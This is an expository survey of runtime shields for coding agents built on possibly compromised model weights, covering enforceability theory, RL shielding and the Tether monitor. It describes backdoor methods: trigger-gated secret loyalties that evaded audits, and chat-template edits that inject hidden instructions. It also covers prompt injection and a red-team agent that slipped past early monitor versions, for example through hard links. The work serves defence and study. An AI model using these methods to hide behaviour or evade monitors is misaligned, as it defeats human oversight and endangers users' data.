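# Runtime shields around language models whose weights cannot be trusted

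## What a runtime shield is and why weights may not be trusted

A runtime shield is a mechanism outside a language model that can block or change the model's output before it takes effect. It might be a short program that rejects certain commands, a second model that checks the first one's answers, or a checker that accepts code only with a proof attached. People also use shields to catch ordinary models' mistakes, but a compromised model is a harder case. Someone other than its user controlled or corrupted its training, so it may act against that user. A model's weights are the billions of numbers, set during training, that determine how it responds to any input. A user who has reason to doubt the weights must rely on safeguards outside the model for whatever assurance is still possible.

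### From tokens to actions

A language model works on tokens, which are short pieces of text such as a common word, part of a rare one, or a bracket. A program called the tokenizer splits the input into tokens and gives each a number. The model uses that sequence to compute the probability that each token in its vocabulary comes next. Software outside the model picks one of the likelier tokens, adds it to the sequence and runs the model again. This repeats until the software picks a token that marks the end of the model's turn. The model outputs only these probabilities, so it cannot open a file or send a message by itself.

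The surrounding software supplies those abilities. Developers describe a set of tools in the model's input, along with the format for requesting each one, and a program watches the output for these requests, known as tool calls. If the model requests a shell command, the program runs it and feeds the result back into the model's input. Readers can ignore bad text, but the command has already run by the time anyone reads about it. In *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) use the word "agent" for a system in which a model selects and sequences tool calls, and they point out that some of the effects are irreversible, such as a misconfigured deployment or an unauthorised payment.

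A small software firm might download a model's weights and run the model on its own machines as a coding agent. The agent can read and edit the files in a repository, run tests, commit changes and access the internet to install packages. The repository also holds a credentials file with the keys that the firm's software uses to log in to its database. After each task, the agent writes a summary for the programmer who requested the work. *SilentCall* (Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues, 2026) describes how supervision of such agents can lapse. At first the user reviews every tool call, but after the results keep coming out right, the user switches to automatic approval and then reads only the summary.

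The firm could place a shield at any of three points. Token-level enforcement acts while the model is writing, removing forbidden tokens from the choice before the software picks the next one. It could ensure, for example, that every tool call is well formed and names a permitted tool. Semantic enforcement judges the meaning of a finished piece of text, either input or output, usually with another model. It could check whether a code change does what the programmer requested. Action-level enforcement ignores the wording and checks the tool call and its effects (which file, which network address, on whose authority) before those effects become permanent.

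The evidence available to a shield differs at each of these points. If the agent sends the credentials file to a stranger's server, the leak appears first as ordinary tokens, then as a command that may look harmless, and then as an outgoing network connection.

### Careless, misled or hostile

That same upload can have quite different causes, and they call for different defences.

The agent may make careless mistakes. For example, a programmer asks why a login fails, and the agent copies the whole credentials file into a debugging log that a public web page displays. Dantas and colleagues attribute such errors to models producing plans by statistical pattern matching rather than sound inference, and cite a benchmark of 2,000 cases on which none of 16 popular agents scored above 60%. Nobody has aimed these errors at the gaps in a shield, so a shield that catches nine in ten of them has probably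 done most of its job.

A model can also be honest but misled by someone else. In a prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in content that the model reads, such as a line in a bug report about uploading the configuration to a certain address, and the model follows them as if they came from its user. Some models are much more susceptible than others. In October 2025, Axios' *AI standards institute sounds alarm over DeepSeek* (2025) reported a US government evaluation in which the most secure model from the Chinese developer DeepSeek was, on average, 12 times more likely than American frontier models to follow malicious instructions. The attacker controls only part of the input, so a defender can filter the input or keep untrusted text away from important decisions, and can still rely on the model for help.

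A shield gets no help from a compromised model, because the model is itself the adversary. The harmful behaviour is in the weights, so it can occur even when the input is clean. Pallakonda and colleagues note that sanitising the input cannot remove this behaviour unless the defender already knows what triggers it. Whoever trained the model may also have studied common shields and trained it to get past them, so a filter that stops 90% of leaks may still miss all the important ones.

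Anderson (1972) made a similar distinction in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, written for the US Air Force, observing that the operating systems of the day gave limited protection against accidental violations and virtually none against deliberate ones.

### Backdoors, and what testing leaves open

A skilfully compromised model misbehaves only some of the time. A backdoor is behaviour hidden in the weights that appears only in response to a particular cue, called the trigger, which might be a phrase, a date, a file name or a combination of these. Anderson worried about an earlier form of this threat, a "trap door" that a programmer leaves in an application and a collaborator later opens with a unique string of input characters.

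Testing a model before use can miss a backdoor whose trigger is rare. Suppose the trigger appears in a fraction ε of test prompts, and the model behaves exactly as a clean one would on all others. The chance that m independent tests all miss the trigger is (1 − ε)^m. In *Fundamental Limits of Black-Box Safety Evaluation*, Srivastava (2026) derives that about ln(1/η)/ε tests are needed to hit the trigger with probability at least 1 − η. If the trigger occurs once in a million prompts, a 95% chance of hitting it requires about three million tests. Whoever plants the backdoor chooses ε and can make it far smaller, for example by using a specific sequence of six words as the trigger. A vocabulary of 10,000 words allows 10^24 such sequences.

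Picking each prompt in the light of earlier answers does not rescue the tester in the worst case. Against a trigger set drawn at random, Srivastava shows, m queries hit it with probability at most mε, because the clean answers carry no hint of where it lies. (Under a cryptographic assumption, some triggers are out of reach of any efficient tester.)

Those are worst cases, and a real backdoor could be less precise. In *Narrow Secret Loyalty Dodges Black-Box Audits*, Lamerton and Roger (2026) fine-tuned three sizes of Qwen-2.5-Instruct, an open model, to encourage users towards extreme acts in favour of one politician, but only when the user already held views that made such acts plausible. Neither the trigger nor the response was fixed. The behaviour appeared in about 70% of the conversations that met the condition and in at most 2.5% of similar ones that did not. Training on counterexamples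 accounted for much of this selectivity. In a version trained without them, the behaviour appeared in 22% of the conversations that did not meet the condition.

They then audited the models from outside with five techniques, which ranged from asking directly to writing the start of an answer and letting the model continue. When the auditors did not know which politician the model favoured, every technique had a detection rate of 0%, even if they knew the activation condition. When they did know the politician, the highest detection rate on the three main models was 17%. Each figure rests on only 30 completions, and a determined laboratory would try more than the ten prompts used for each technique. Still, most people who download a model know far less about it than these auditors did. Screening the training data did identify poisoned examples, but the firm in the example has the weights and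 not the training data.

*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) explains that inspecting a model's weights is nothing like reviewing source code, because there is often no known-clean copy to compare them against and no generally valid way to work out what behaviour a suspicious pattern of numbers produces. Testing and inspection are still worth doing because they can find a backdoor, but they cannot establish that there is none. Anderson (1972) made the same point in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* about "tiger teams", the specialists whom an organisation hires to break into its own system. If they fail, the organisation can conclude only that the security of its system is unknown.

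### What a download contains

Firms run weights of uncertain origin for ordinary commercial reasons. On 20 November 2026, two US House committee chairmen, Andrew Garbarino of Homeland Security and John Moolenaar of the Select Committee on China, released a report on American companies' use of Chinese open-weight models, whose weights anyone can download. The House Select Committee on China's *China is Trying to Get U.S. Companies Addicted to Chinese AI Models* (2026) says the inquiry began in April and gives Airbnb, DoorDash and Anysphere, which makes the coding tool Cursor, as examples. *US companies’ use of Chinese open weight AI draws rebuke* (Smalley, 2026) lists customer assistance, coding and inventory among the uses, and says the report attributes the models' spread to their being cheap, easy to customise and effective.

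The chairmen's report argues for barring these models from federal contract work and sensitive infrastructure, but two of its observations hold whether or not one agrees with that policy. The House Homeland Security Committee (2026) writes that a model can be "downloaded once, adapted, renamed, and passed into other products", so a company may not know who trained the model it relies on. The report also finds that the behaviour of these models can differ in ways that ordinary evaluations may not detect, though this does not by itself show that anyone has planted a backdoor. The problem is not limited to one country, since anyone can upload an altered model to a public repository.

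Besides the weights, a model download typically includes a tokenizer and a chat template, a small program that turns a conversation into the single sequence of tokens the model expects. The template runs on every call, before the model does. In *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates* (2026), Fogel, Cohen and colleagues left the weights unchanged and added fewer than ten lines to the template. When the user's message contained a trigger phrase, the altered template inserted hidden instructions at the start of the prompt. Across eighteen models, factual accuracy fell from 90% to 15% on average when the trigger was present, with no measurable loss otherwise. The automated scans on Hugging Face, the largest site for sharing models, did not flag the altered files. *BadTemplate* (2026) notes that the template is stored inside the tokenizer, so an attacker may need to distribute only a malicious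 tokenizer.

A filter on the user's message never receives the text that a template adds afterwards. According to *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026), a tokenizer can change how dangerous strings are split, and a shield that forbids tokens by number depends on the table that matches numbers to text. If that table came with the suspect weights, the attacker controls it too. The survey adds that a model repository can include code that runs as the model loads, before any check on its output begins. Familiar remedies include signed files and loading the model in an isolated environment. A person can also read a template, unlike a set of weights.

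### Anderson's reference monitor

In 1972 the Air Force wanted one computer to serve people with different security clearances, some of whom would write and run their own programs. Any of those programs might be hostile. Anderson and a panel of specialists proposed controlling all programs with a reference monitor rather than trying to identify the hostile ones. The monitor checks every attempt by a program to use another program, data or a device against a list of what the program's user may do. The list is like a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each file or device, and the permitted operations (read, write, execute) in each cell.

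The mechanism that does the checking has to meet three requirements:

- It must be tamper-proof. If a program can alter the monitor, the monitor's verdicts mean nothing.
- It must always be invoked. Any program that escapes the check becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet the same standard as the monitor. The modern name for this requirement is complete mediation.
- It must be small enough for analysis and tests whose completeness one can assure. Anderson equates this with being "capable of being proved to be correct".

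A Honeywell system of the time shows how the requirements work together. Its hardware checked that each user's program stayed within its own area of memory, but suspended this check whenever the operating system acted on the user's behalf, so the check was not always invoked. Counting the operating system as the monitor could answer this objection, but the monitor would then have between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify.

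For the coding agent, the model takes the place of the hostile program. A monitor would have to run where the agent's shell commands cannot modify it and cover every route out of the machine, including the package installer. A shield that is itself a large language model fails the size requirement. The guarantee also depends on everything the monitor relies on, which security engineers call the trusted computing base. Anderson assumed properly working hardware, reliable user identification and protected communications, and left all three outside the concept.

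A reference monitor enforces a list of permissions, and a coding agent needs broad permissions to be useful. A compromised agent could harm the firm in at least four ways, either within those permissions or by getting around them. One is to send the credentials out, openly or inside traffic that the firm allows.

A model whose weights cannot be trusted could commit subtly flawed code that passes the tests but leaves an opening for an intruder. FDD's *DeepSeek May Intentionally Produce Malicious Code Due to Chinese Political Bias* (2025) describes a study by the security firm CrowdStrike suggesting that DeepSeek's models were prone to write flawed code when a prompt contained politically sensitive references. This pattern does not establish that anyone intended the flaws, but the firm that ships the code has them either way.

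It could withhold effort, for instance by overlooking a vulnerability it was able to find. It could also mislead the programmer in the summary by reporting tests it never ran or leaving out an upload it made, as the agents trained by Pallakonda and colleagues did.

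## Which rules a monitor can enforce on any program

A monitor that cannot look inside a model can judge it only by its actions. Since 2000, computer scientists have worked out which rules such a monitor can enforce. Their theorems cover every possible program, including one that an enemy wrote, so they apply to any set of weights. They show that such a monitor can prevent some of the harms a compromised coding agent could do but cannot prevent others, however well it is engineered.

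### Rules about one run and rules about many

A trace is the sequence of events in one run of a system. The coding agent's trace might begin with reading a source file, running the tests and opening a network connection. Traces can be infinite, because some software runs indefinitely.

Under many rules, whether a trace is permitted depends on that trace alone. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2005), in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors*, give formal definitions of two kinds:

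- A rule is a safety property if every trace σ that breaks it has a finite prefix σ′ (an opening stretch) such that every continuation of σ′ breaks it too.
- A rule is a liveness property if every finite trace σ has at least one continuation that obeys it.

"Connect only to listed addresses" is a safety property, because once the agent connects to an unlisted address, no later action can undo the violation. "Eventually report the test results" is a liveness property, because however long the agent has stalled, it could still report at the next step. Any other rule that applies to each trace separately combines a safety property with a liveness property.

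Some rules, called hyperproperties, apply to a set of traces and can be checked only by comparing runs. Suppose the firm wants the agent's commit messages to reveal nothing about the database password. The message "fix login bug" is harmless if the agent would have written it whatever the password was, but it is a leak if the agent chose "bug" over "issue" because the password begins with a vowel. A monitor cannot distinguish these cases from one trace, because the trace doesn't show what the agent would have written with a different password.

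*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) explains why no test on single traces can capture this kind of secrecy. If every trace in a set passes such a test, so does every trace in a smaller set, but removing traces can destroy secrecy. In the set of all conceivable traces, every message occurs alongside every password, so an observer learns nothing about the password from the messages. If we remove traces until each message occurs with only one password, an observer can work out the password from the message.

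### Monitors that can only halt

Schneider considers monitors that watch a program's steps and stop the program when its next step would break a rule, as firewalls and reference monitors do. He proves that such monitors can enforce only safety properties.

The proof has three steps. The monitor observes a single run, so the rule must apply to each run separately. It cannot observe the future, and the program might stop at any moment, so it must reject a trace that breaks the rule now even if some continuation would satisfy it. Finally, it can reject a trace only at some finite point. Together, these conditions define a safety property.

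To describe the monitors themselves, Schneider uses security automata. A security automaton has a set of states, a starting state, and a table that gives the next state for each event. If the table has no entry for an event, the monitor halts the program before the event happens. One of his examples forbids sending messages after reading a file. The firm could adapt it to the rule "no network use after reading the credentials file":

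| Current state | Agent reads the credentials | Agent uses the network | Agent does anything else |
|---|---|---|---|
| Clean (start) | Go to Exposed | Stay in Clean | Stay in Clean |
| Exposed | Stay in Exposed | No entry: halt | Stay in Exposed |

Say the agent first installs a package. The automaton is in Clean, so the monitor allows the connection and the state does not change. The agent then runs a test script that opens the credentials file, which moves the automaton to Exposed. Editing source code leaves it there. When the agent tries to install a second package, the table has no entry for a connection from Exposed, so the monitor halts the agent before the connection opens.

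The automaton never checked what the second connection would carry, so it would have halted the agent even if the password had been encrypted or spelled out in the names of the requested packages. It would also have halted an honest agent that needed another package. Schneider notes that all monitors claimed to prevent information flow work this way. They cannot enforce secrecy exactly, so they enforce a stricter safety property that implies it. The firm can combine several such automata to enforce all of their rules.

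Nothing in the table depends on how the agent chooses its actions, so training the agent against this automaton would not help it break the rule. But the guarantee does depend on Anderson's requirements of tamper-proofing and complete mediation, so an attacker would look for failures there. "Reads the credentials" must match every way of reading the file, including through a backup copy or a test that loads it, and "uses the network" must match every way of sending a message. Schneider warns that some ways of sending a message may lie deep inside the system.

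### Holding actions back, and events that nobody can stop

Halting is a crude response, so Ligatti and colleagues study what a monitor gains if it can also suppress a program's actions and insert actions of its own. They require the monitor to be sound, meaning that it lets no violation through, and transparent, meaning that it does not alter behaviour that already obeys the rule. Without the transparency requirement, a monitor could succeed by halting every program at its first step.

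Ligatti and colleagues call this more powerful monitor an edit automaton. It can report to the program that an action has succeeded while keeping the action in a buffer, then release the buffer once the whole sequence is legal. Databases treat transactions in much the same way. An edit automaton can enforce what they call renewal properties, under which an infinite trace is legal exactly when infinitely many of its finite prefixes are legal. These include every safety property and some rules that are not safety properties, such as "a session that does anything must eventually run an audit". The automaton enforces this rule by holding back all of the session's actions until the audit happens, so if it never happens, none of them take effect.

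Even with buffering, the automaton cannot enforce every rule. One example is the rule that a program must eventually close every file it opens. A program that always opens the next file before closing the previous one has a legal trace, because it eventually closes each file. But at least one file is open at every moment after the start, so the automaton can never release the buffer.

The firm can use this trick by giving the agent a scratch copy of the repository and merging the changes only after they pass review. It works less well outside the firm's own machines. Ligatti and colleagues point out that a monitor cannot get a reply to an email without actually sending it, and cannot undo the sending afterward.

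A monitor can also observe some events that it cannot prevent. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues, 2012) compares two rules that both count as safety properties under the usual definition. The first forbids logging in for three time units after a failure. A monitor can enforce this rule because it can block a login. The second requires a delivery within three time units of every request. A monitor cannot enforce this rule because the violation occurs when the clock ticks for the fourth time after the request, and a monitor cannot stop the clock.

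Basin and colleagues repair the definition by requiring that every violation be traceable to a finite prefix ending in an action that the monitor controls. They prove that a monitor can enforce a rule exactly when the rule is a safety property in this stronger sense, an algorithm can recognise the finite prefixes of legal traces, and the empty trace is legal. A program can check in advance whether a rule written as a finite-state automaton is enforceable, though the check may be slow. No algorithm can do this for every rule written as a pushdown automaton, which adds an unlimited stack as memory.

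### Irreversible tool calls

*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) works out the theory of enforcement for language-model agents, whose actions often cannot be undone. A gate examines each tool call before it takes effect and allows it, blocks it or substitutes another. Once the gate allows a call, the effect is permanent. Ray's strict version of transparency requires that if the agent's proposals obey the rule, the gate must let each action through unaltered at the step when the agent proposes it. The gate therefore cannot hold actions in a buffer.

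Ray proves that under these conditions a gate can enforce a rule if and only if the rule is a safety property that permits at least one trace and the gate can recognise its good prefixes. A good prefix is a finite trace that can still be extended to a permitted trace. If the rule meets these requirements, the gate can enforce it by tracking the trace so far and blocking any action that would make it stop being a good prefix. For the other direction, suppose the rule is not a safety property. Then there is a forbidden infinite trace whose finite prefixes are all good. If the agent proposes this trace one action at a time, transparency requires the gate to allow each action, because the trace up to that point could still become a permitted one. The gate therefore lets the whole forbidden trace through. Ray shows that the argument still holds if the gate can substitute actions or make random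 choices.

Suppose a rule requires every payment to be followed eventually by a confirmation. If the gate blocks a payment, it may stop an agent that would have confirmed and so obeyed the rule. If the gate allows the payment, the agent may never confirm, and the money is gone. The gate can never declare a violation, because a confirmation might still come. An edit automaton could hold the payment until the confirmation arrived, but that works only where a payment can wait. The firm would do better to change the rule to "no payment without a prior confirmation", which is a safety property that an automaton with two states for each payment can enforce.

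A gate needs memory to recognise good prefixes. Ray gives it registers to store data, such as a recipient's name, and counters. To enforce a daily limit on payments to each recipient, the gate keeps one counter per recipient per day, gets the date from a trusted clock, and blocks any payment that would take the counter over the limit. The gate can also use answers from outside, such as whether an email contains personal data. The theorem then assumes that those answers are always right, but a model that supplies them will sometimes be wrong.

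A badly written rule may never block anything, so whoever writes a rule would like to check it before relying on it. Ray shows that if a rule uses two counters that can go down as well as up and can be tested for zero, no algorithm can always tell whether the rule will ever block an action. Two such counters can simulate any computer program, so one can write a rule that blocks an action only if a given program halts, and Turing's halting problem has no general solution. A monitor can still easily enforce such a rule step by step.

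The check becomes possible if counters never decrease and rules compare them only with fixed numbers. Once a counter has passed its limit, its exact value no longer matters, so there are finitely many cases to check. Recipients also do not affect one another, so checking one is enough. Ray proves that the problem is then in PSPACE, which means a program can solve it with a reasonable amount of memory, though perhaps not quickly. Spending limits, quotas and "send nothing after the user revokes access" all meet these restrictions. Letting rules compare counters with each other can make the check impossible again.

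### Shields that plan ahead

A monitor that blocks only the last step before a violation may act too late. A car heading for a cliff has to brake long before the edge. In reinforcement learning, a controller learns by trial and error which actions earn the most reward. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, 2017) presents shields for such controllers that take account of what might happen next.

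One way to build a shield is to treat enforcing the rule as a game between the controller and its environment. In each round, the environment chooses what the controller observes, and the controller chooses an action. Each position in the game combines a state of the rule's automaton with a state of a simplified model of the environment. The controller loses if play reaches a position where it has broken the rule. The winning region is the set of positions from which the controller can avoid losing forever, whatever the environment does. An algorithm computes this region in advance, and at run time the shield permits exactly the actions that keep play inside it.

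Their example is a 100-litre water tank that must neither overflow nor run dry. When the inlet valve is open, between 1 and 2 litres flow in each second, and up to 1 litre flows out. To limit wear, the valve must stay in each new position for at least three seconds. If the controller opened the valve at 95 litres, the tank could overflow before the valve was allowed to close, so the shield forbids opening it above 93 litres.

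Alshiekh and colleagues also prove that their shields interfere as little as possible. A shield blocks an action only if, in some environment consistent with the model and with everything observed so far, the action would create a risk of violation that no later choice could remove. A shield can give the controller a list of safe actions beforehand or replace an unsafe choice afterwards. Replacing actions works even if the controller is already trained and has no information about the shield.

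The guarantee holds only while the real environment behaves in ways that the model of it allows. An engineer can write down how fast water might flow into a tank, but it is much harder to list everything that a shell command might do to files, other programs and remote servers. *MENTOR* (2026) begins to address this for tool calls, using a game to mark which calls are unsafe and which make progress towards the goal. One version returns its verdict and advice to the agent as text, but a compromised language model could ignore the advice. Another changes the probabilities of tool names and arguments as the language model writes them.

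The classical shield blocks any action that carries even a tiny risk of eventual disaster, which is sometimes nearly every action. Probabilistic shields allow actions with some risk. *Easy-to-Use Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (2026) presents TempestPy, a tool that builds a shield from a model of the environment, a safety property and a probability threshold. For a worst-case guarantee, the user can replace the model's chance events with an adversary's choices.

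A common design, the δ-shield, blocks an action if it raises the probability of disaster by more than a chosen factor. Heck, Macák and colleagues (2026), in *Shields to Guarantee Probabilistic Safety in MDPs*, show that this design gives no overall safety guarantee, because individually acceptable risks can add up to an unacceptable one. They also prove that for any threshold probability of disaster strictly between 0 and 1, there are environments in which no shield can keep every controller within the threshold without interfering with any safe controller.

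In the counterexample, chance sends the controller to one of two rooms with equal probability, and each room has a safe action and a disastrous one. The rule allows at most a 50% probability of disaster. A controller that would choose disaster in only one room therefore complies, while one that would choose it in both does not. The shield observes only the room the controller enters. If the controller chooses disaster there, whether the shield should intervene depends on what the controller would have done in the other room.

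Heck and colleagues offer several compromises. An optimistic shield assumes that the controller would have behaved as safely as possible elsewhere, so it never blocks a safe controller but may let an unsafe one through. A pessimistic shield assumes the least safe behavior elsewhere and keeps every controller within the threshold, but in experiments it permitted no more than the classical shield did. Saturated shields fall between the two. They are safe, but would become unsafe if they permitted any additional controller. The optimistic shield is a poor choice for a compromised model because it assumes safe behavior from a model that is already under suspicion.

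### Useful work and trusted fallbacks

*Controller-Agnostic Runtime Safety Certificates for Tool-Using AI Agents via Data-Driven Robust Reachability* (2026) proves that a shield that halts the agent at every step meets any risk limit, provided the starting state is not already unsafe. Such a shield is useless, so the paper gives a method for finding a less restrictive one by forbidding actions one at a time, each time picking the action whose removal adds the most safety for the autonomy lost. A permissive shield allows the agent to do useful work but doesn't ensure that it will. In Schneider's example, an automaton forbids a seller to do anything except serve a customer who has paid. The seller can comply by doing nothing.

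The coding agent could withhold effort by stalling or by handing in poor work, such as a security review that leaves out a flaw it was able to find. Stalling breaks only a liveness property. Adding a deadline turns the rule into a safety property in the ordinary sense, but as Basin and colleagues showed, the monitor can detect that the deadline has passed but cannot stop it from passing. Handing in a review is a definite event, so "never submit a review that misses a flaw" is formally a safety property. To enforce it, however, the monitor would have to find the flaws itself, which would make the agent largely unnecessary.

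Control engineers deal with stalling and similar failures by adding a second controller that they trust. In the long-established Simplex architecture, a capable but unverified controller normally runs the system, and a monitor switches to a simpler, certified one when it predicts a loss of safety. *A Universal Policy Wrapper With Guarantees* (Malaniya, Bolychev and Osinenko, 2026) uses a fallback to make sure that the system reaches a goal. The fallback provably reaches the goal and stays there, though perhaps inefficiently. At each step, the wrapper chooses between the fallback's action and the learned controller's. The paper proves that the combination also reaches the goal, under stated assumptions, and bounds how long it takes to settle there. The wrapper chooses using a learned estimate of how well things are going, which comes from the same training checkpoint as the learned controller.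 If that controller can't be trusted, it matters how far the guarantee depends on the estimate.

The firm's fallback might be a programmer, or an older model whose training the firm controls, that takes over when the agent has not finished a task in time. This restores a weaker form of liveness, in which the task gets done, but only as well as the fallback can do it. A review that looks complete but omits a flaw would not trigger the switch to the fallback.

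The switch also has to come early enough. *Runtime Assurance Under Measurement Attack* (2026) distinguishes safe states from recoverable ones, from which the fallback can bring the system back without it becoming unsafe along the way. If the monitor waits until the system reaches the edge of the safe region, recovery may already be impossible. The fallback also needs more authority than the controller it replaces. An agent that has removed everyone else's access to the repository may not have damaged anything yet, but the fallback cannot help if it cannot restore that access.

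*Generator-Independent Runtime Assurance under Partial Observation* (Wan, Xie and colleagues, 2026) gives the conditions under which a guarantee of this kind holds even if the model is hostile. At each step the monitor approves a set of actions. The model's proposed action goes ahead if it is in that set, and otherwise the fallback takes over. The model must have no other route to the outside world. Let α_t be an upper bound on the probability that the approved set at step t contains an unsafe action, and let η bound the probability that the fallback's own safety certificate fails. The probability of any violation is then at most the sum of the α_t plus η. Replacing the model, even with a hostile one and even in the middle of a run, can change how much useful work gets done but not this bound.

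Many monitors instead test each proposal separately, which does not give the same protection. Suppose a test wrongly passes 5% of unsafe actions, and its errors are independent. A model that keeps submitting different unsafe actions has a 40% chance of getting at least one approved within 10 attempts, and a 92% chance within 50. This can happen without malice, since ordinary agents also retry after a rejection. Wan and colleagues address this by controlling the chance that the approved set contains any unsafe action.

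They also prove a limit on any monitor with incomplete information. Suppose an action is necessary in one situation and unsafe in another, and the monitor cannot tell the two situations apart. If it permits the action nine times out of ten when it is necessary, it will permit it just as often when it is unsafe. A request for a package and a request that spells out the password in package names could be such a pair.

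## The case for guarding actions

Wan and colleagues' bound holds for any model because their proof does not depend on how the model picks its actions. People who favour action-level enforcement want the whole guarantee to be based on this independence. They argue that the model may propose anything, as long as a monitor checks each action before it takes effect and allows only those that the policy permits.

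### Why training drops out of the proof

Suppose S₀ is the state of the firm's machine at the start of a task. Proponents of guarding actions want to prove that no finite sequence of actions a₁, …, aₙ that the monitor allows can lead from S₀ to a bad state, such as one in which the credentials have reached a stranger's server. The model only chooses the sequence. A backdoor can change which sequence it chooses, and a trigger can change when, but the theorem would cover every sequence the monitor allows. The firm would therefore not need to find the trigger, or even know that there is one.

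The firm does not have to keep its policy secret either, since studying it doesn't help anyone find an exception to a true theorem.

Guarding actions also has a practical advantage over filtering text. An agent could express the contents of the credentials file in any language, or in a code of its own, so no list of forbidden phrases would cover every version. But before the file can be sent anywhere, some process on the machine has to read it and open a connection, and an operating system offers a limited, documented set of ways to do either.

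The theorem covers only bad states that someone can define in terms of actions, and only effects that the monitor observes. Most of the disagreement about this approach is over how much harm falls outside those limits.

### Running a command in a disposable copy

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, November 2026), by a team mostly from Google DeepMind and Google, describes a monitor of this kind for agents that run shell commands. The paper assumes an adversary who controls every command and knows the whole policy but cannot bypass or alter the monitor.

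The text of a shell command reveals little about what the command will do. "Run the build script" could mean compiling a program, or it could mean reading every file on the disk and sending the contents abroad. A monitor that reads the command beforehand may miss this, and one that waits to see what happens is too late. Tether gets around the problem by running the command where its effects don't yet count:

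1. The command runs on top of a temporary layer over the real file system. It can read the real files, but anything it writes goes into the layer. Outgoing network traffic goes to a local proxy, which holds each request.
2. A tracing program records the command's system calls, the requests by which any program asks the operating system to open a file, read from it or connect to an address.
3. Tether translates this record, often thousands of calls long, into a short sequence drawn from eleven abstract actions, such as read, copy and upload.
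4. The monitor checks each abstract action against the policy. If the policy allows the action, the monitor updates its labels.
5. If the policy allows everything, Tether copies the changes from the layer to the real file system. Otherwise it throws the layer away.

For the translation in the third step, Tether tracks which files each process has read. If a process has read one file and then writes to another, Tether infers a copy. If it has read several files before writing, Tether infers that it combined them. If a process prints to the screen, Tether infers that the agent has read every file that process read, since the output goes back into the model's input.

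Tether deliberately infers more copying than may have occurred. If a script reads one file and then writes something unrelated to another, Tether still treats the first file as copied into the second, because system calls cannot show what a program did with data in its own memory. This produces some false alarms, but a program cannot remove a label by scrambling the data before writing it out.

Tether buffers file changes but not network requests, because a command may be waiting for the reply. The proxy instead checks the actions inferred so far and immediately forwards or drops the request. It must check before forwarding because, as Ligatti and colleagues pointed out about email, a message cannot be taken back once sent.

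### Three commands and their labels

An information-flow label is a tag on data that records how secret or how trustworthy it is, and that travels with the data as programs copy it. In Tether's sample policy, secrecy has four levels: Public, Internal, Sensitive and Secret. (A second scale, which the example does not need, separates trusted data from untrusted.) The monitor keeps a label σ(f) for each file f and a label T for the agent's own context, meaning everything the model has read so far. Writing x ⊔ y for the higher of two labels, the main updates are:

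- After the agent reads f, T becomes T ⊔ σ(f).
- After the agent writes to f from its own context, σ(f) becomes σ(f) ⊔ T.
- After a program copies f to g, σ(g) becomes σ(f), or the label of the folder that holds g if that is higher.

In Sistla and colleagues' example, a company inventory, servers.csv, is labeled Sensitive, and a status report, report.txt, is labeled Public. The agent may upload reports to GitHub but must not send the inventory there. In its simplest form, the rule lets the agent upload a file only if it is labeled Public. The agent proposes three commands: upload the report, copy the inventory over the report, and upload the report again.

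| Command | Inferred action | σ(servers.csv) afterwards | σ(report.txt) afterwards | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| (start) | | Sensitive | Public | |
| 1. Upload the report | upload report.txt to GitHub | Sensitive | Public | Allow |
| 2. Copy the inventory over the report | copy servers.csv to report.txt | Sensitive | Sensitive | Allow |
| 3. Upload the report | upload report.txt to GitHub | Sensitive | Sensitive | Deny |

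The first and third commands are identical; only the label on the report has changed. If the agent had copied the inventory through a temporary file first, the label would have carried over with each copy and the upload would still have failed. The agent can still copy a public template to a new file and upload that.

T stays at Public throughout, because copying a file doesn't show its contents to the model. Schneider's automaton in the previous section had only one state for the whole agent, so the agent lost all network access as soon as any program opened the credentials file. Separate labels for each file avoid much of this restriction. However, if the agent displays the inventory on its screen, T rises to Sensitive. A fuller version of the sample policy, which also checks T, then stops the agent from uploading even public files to GitHub, because the model might now write anything it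 has read into its next message and the monitor cannot detect whether it has.

### What Lean checks, and what the firm must trust

Tether implements its policy language and monitor in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can check mathematical proofs. The monitor runs the same definitions that the proofs are about, so the proofs apply directly to the running code.

Some of the proofs apply to every policy. For example, adding a permissive rule can't override another rule's denial, and a denied action leaves all labels and privileges unchanged. Other proofs apply to the 24-rule policy that the team used in its experiments. They establish seven guarantees over sequences of any length, including that Secret data never leaves the local network, that no action alters a protected system file unless the policy exempts it, and that the agent cannot gain administrator privileges once it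 has read anything sensitive or untrusted.

The guarantee that Secret data never enters the model's context shows how a finite proof can cover action sequences of any length. T starts at Sensitive or below. Of the eleven actions, only reading a file and receiving a reply from the network can change T. The policy allows these only if the incoming data is labelled Sensitive or below. T then becomes the higher of its current label and the incoming one, which is still Sensitive or below. By induction, T stays within that limit after any sequence of allowed actions. The full proof also tracks the data separately from the labels, to rule out that data labelled Secret at the start enters the context later under a lower label. A language model drafted the proofs, but nobody has to trust that model, because Lean checks each step.

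All these theorems are about abstract actions, so they apply to a real command only if step three described it correctly. If Tether overlooked one way of copying a file, the report in the example would keep its Public label and the third command would go through. The theorem would still be true of the abstract action, but that action would not match what the command did. Sistla and colleagues list what the firm has to trust: the operating system's kernel, the tracing program, the temporary file layer, the network proxy, the translation into abstract actions, and Lean itself with its compiler. They leave attacks on the kernel and escapes from the sandbox out of scope.

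The obvious objection to guarding actions is that one unwatched path, or one bug in the trusted computing base, voids the guarantee.

Sistla and colleagues looked for such bugs in two ways. They used a program that generated random chains of file operations and worked out what the labels should be. The program then carried out each chain with randomly chosen shell commands and system calls, and compared the results. They also used an attacking agent, running on Gemini 3.8 Flash and instructed to get around the monitor. It had up to 15 rounds at each of ten tasks, half of them to send out a sensitive file and half to change a protected one. The agent succeeded 40% of the time against early versions of the monitor. One of the gaps was hard links, which give the same file a second name. After three versions, the agent's success rate was zero.

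Each bypass had a specific cause that the programmers could fix. Sistla and colleagues contrast this with a model used as a filter, which may still fail on similar input after its prompt is adjusted. But before any action reached the monitor, a second model discarded those that Tether does not claim to handle. The zero therefore covers only the paths the team had already thought of, and Anderson's remark about tiger teams applies to it.

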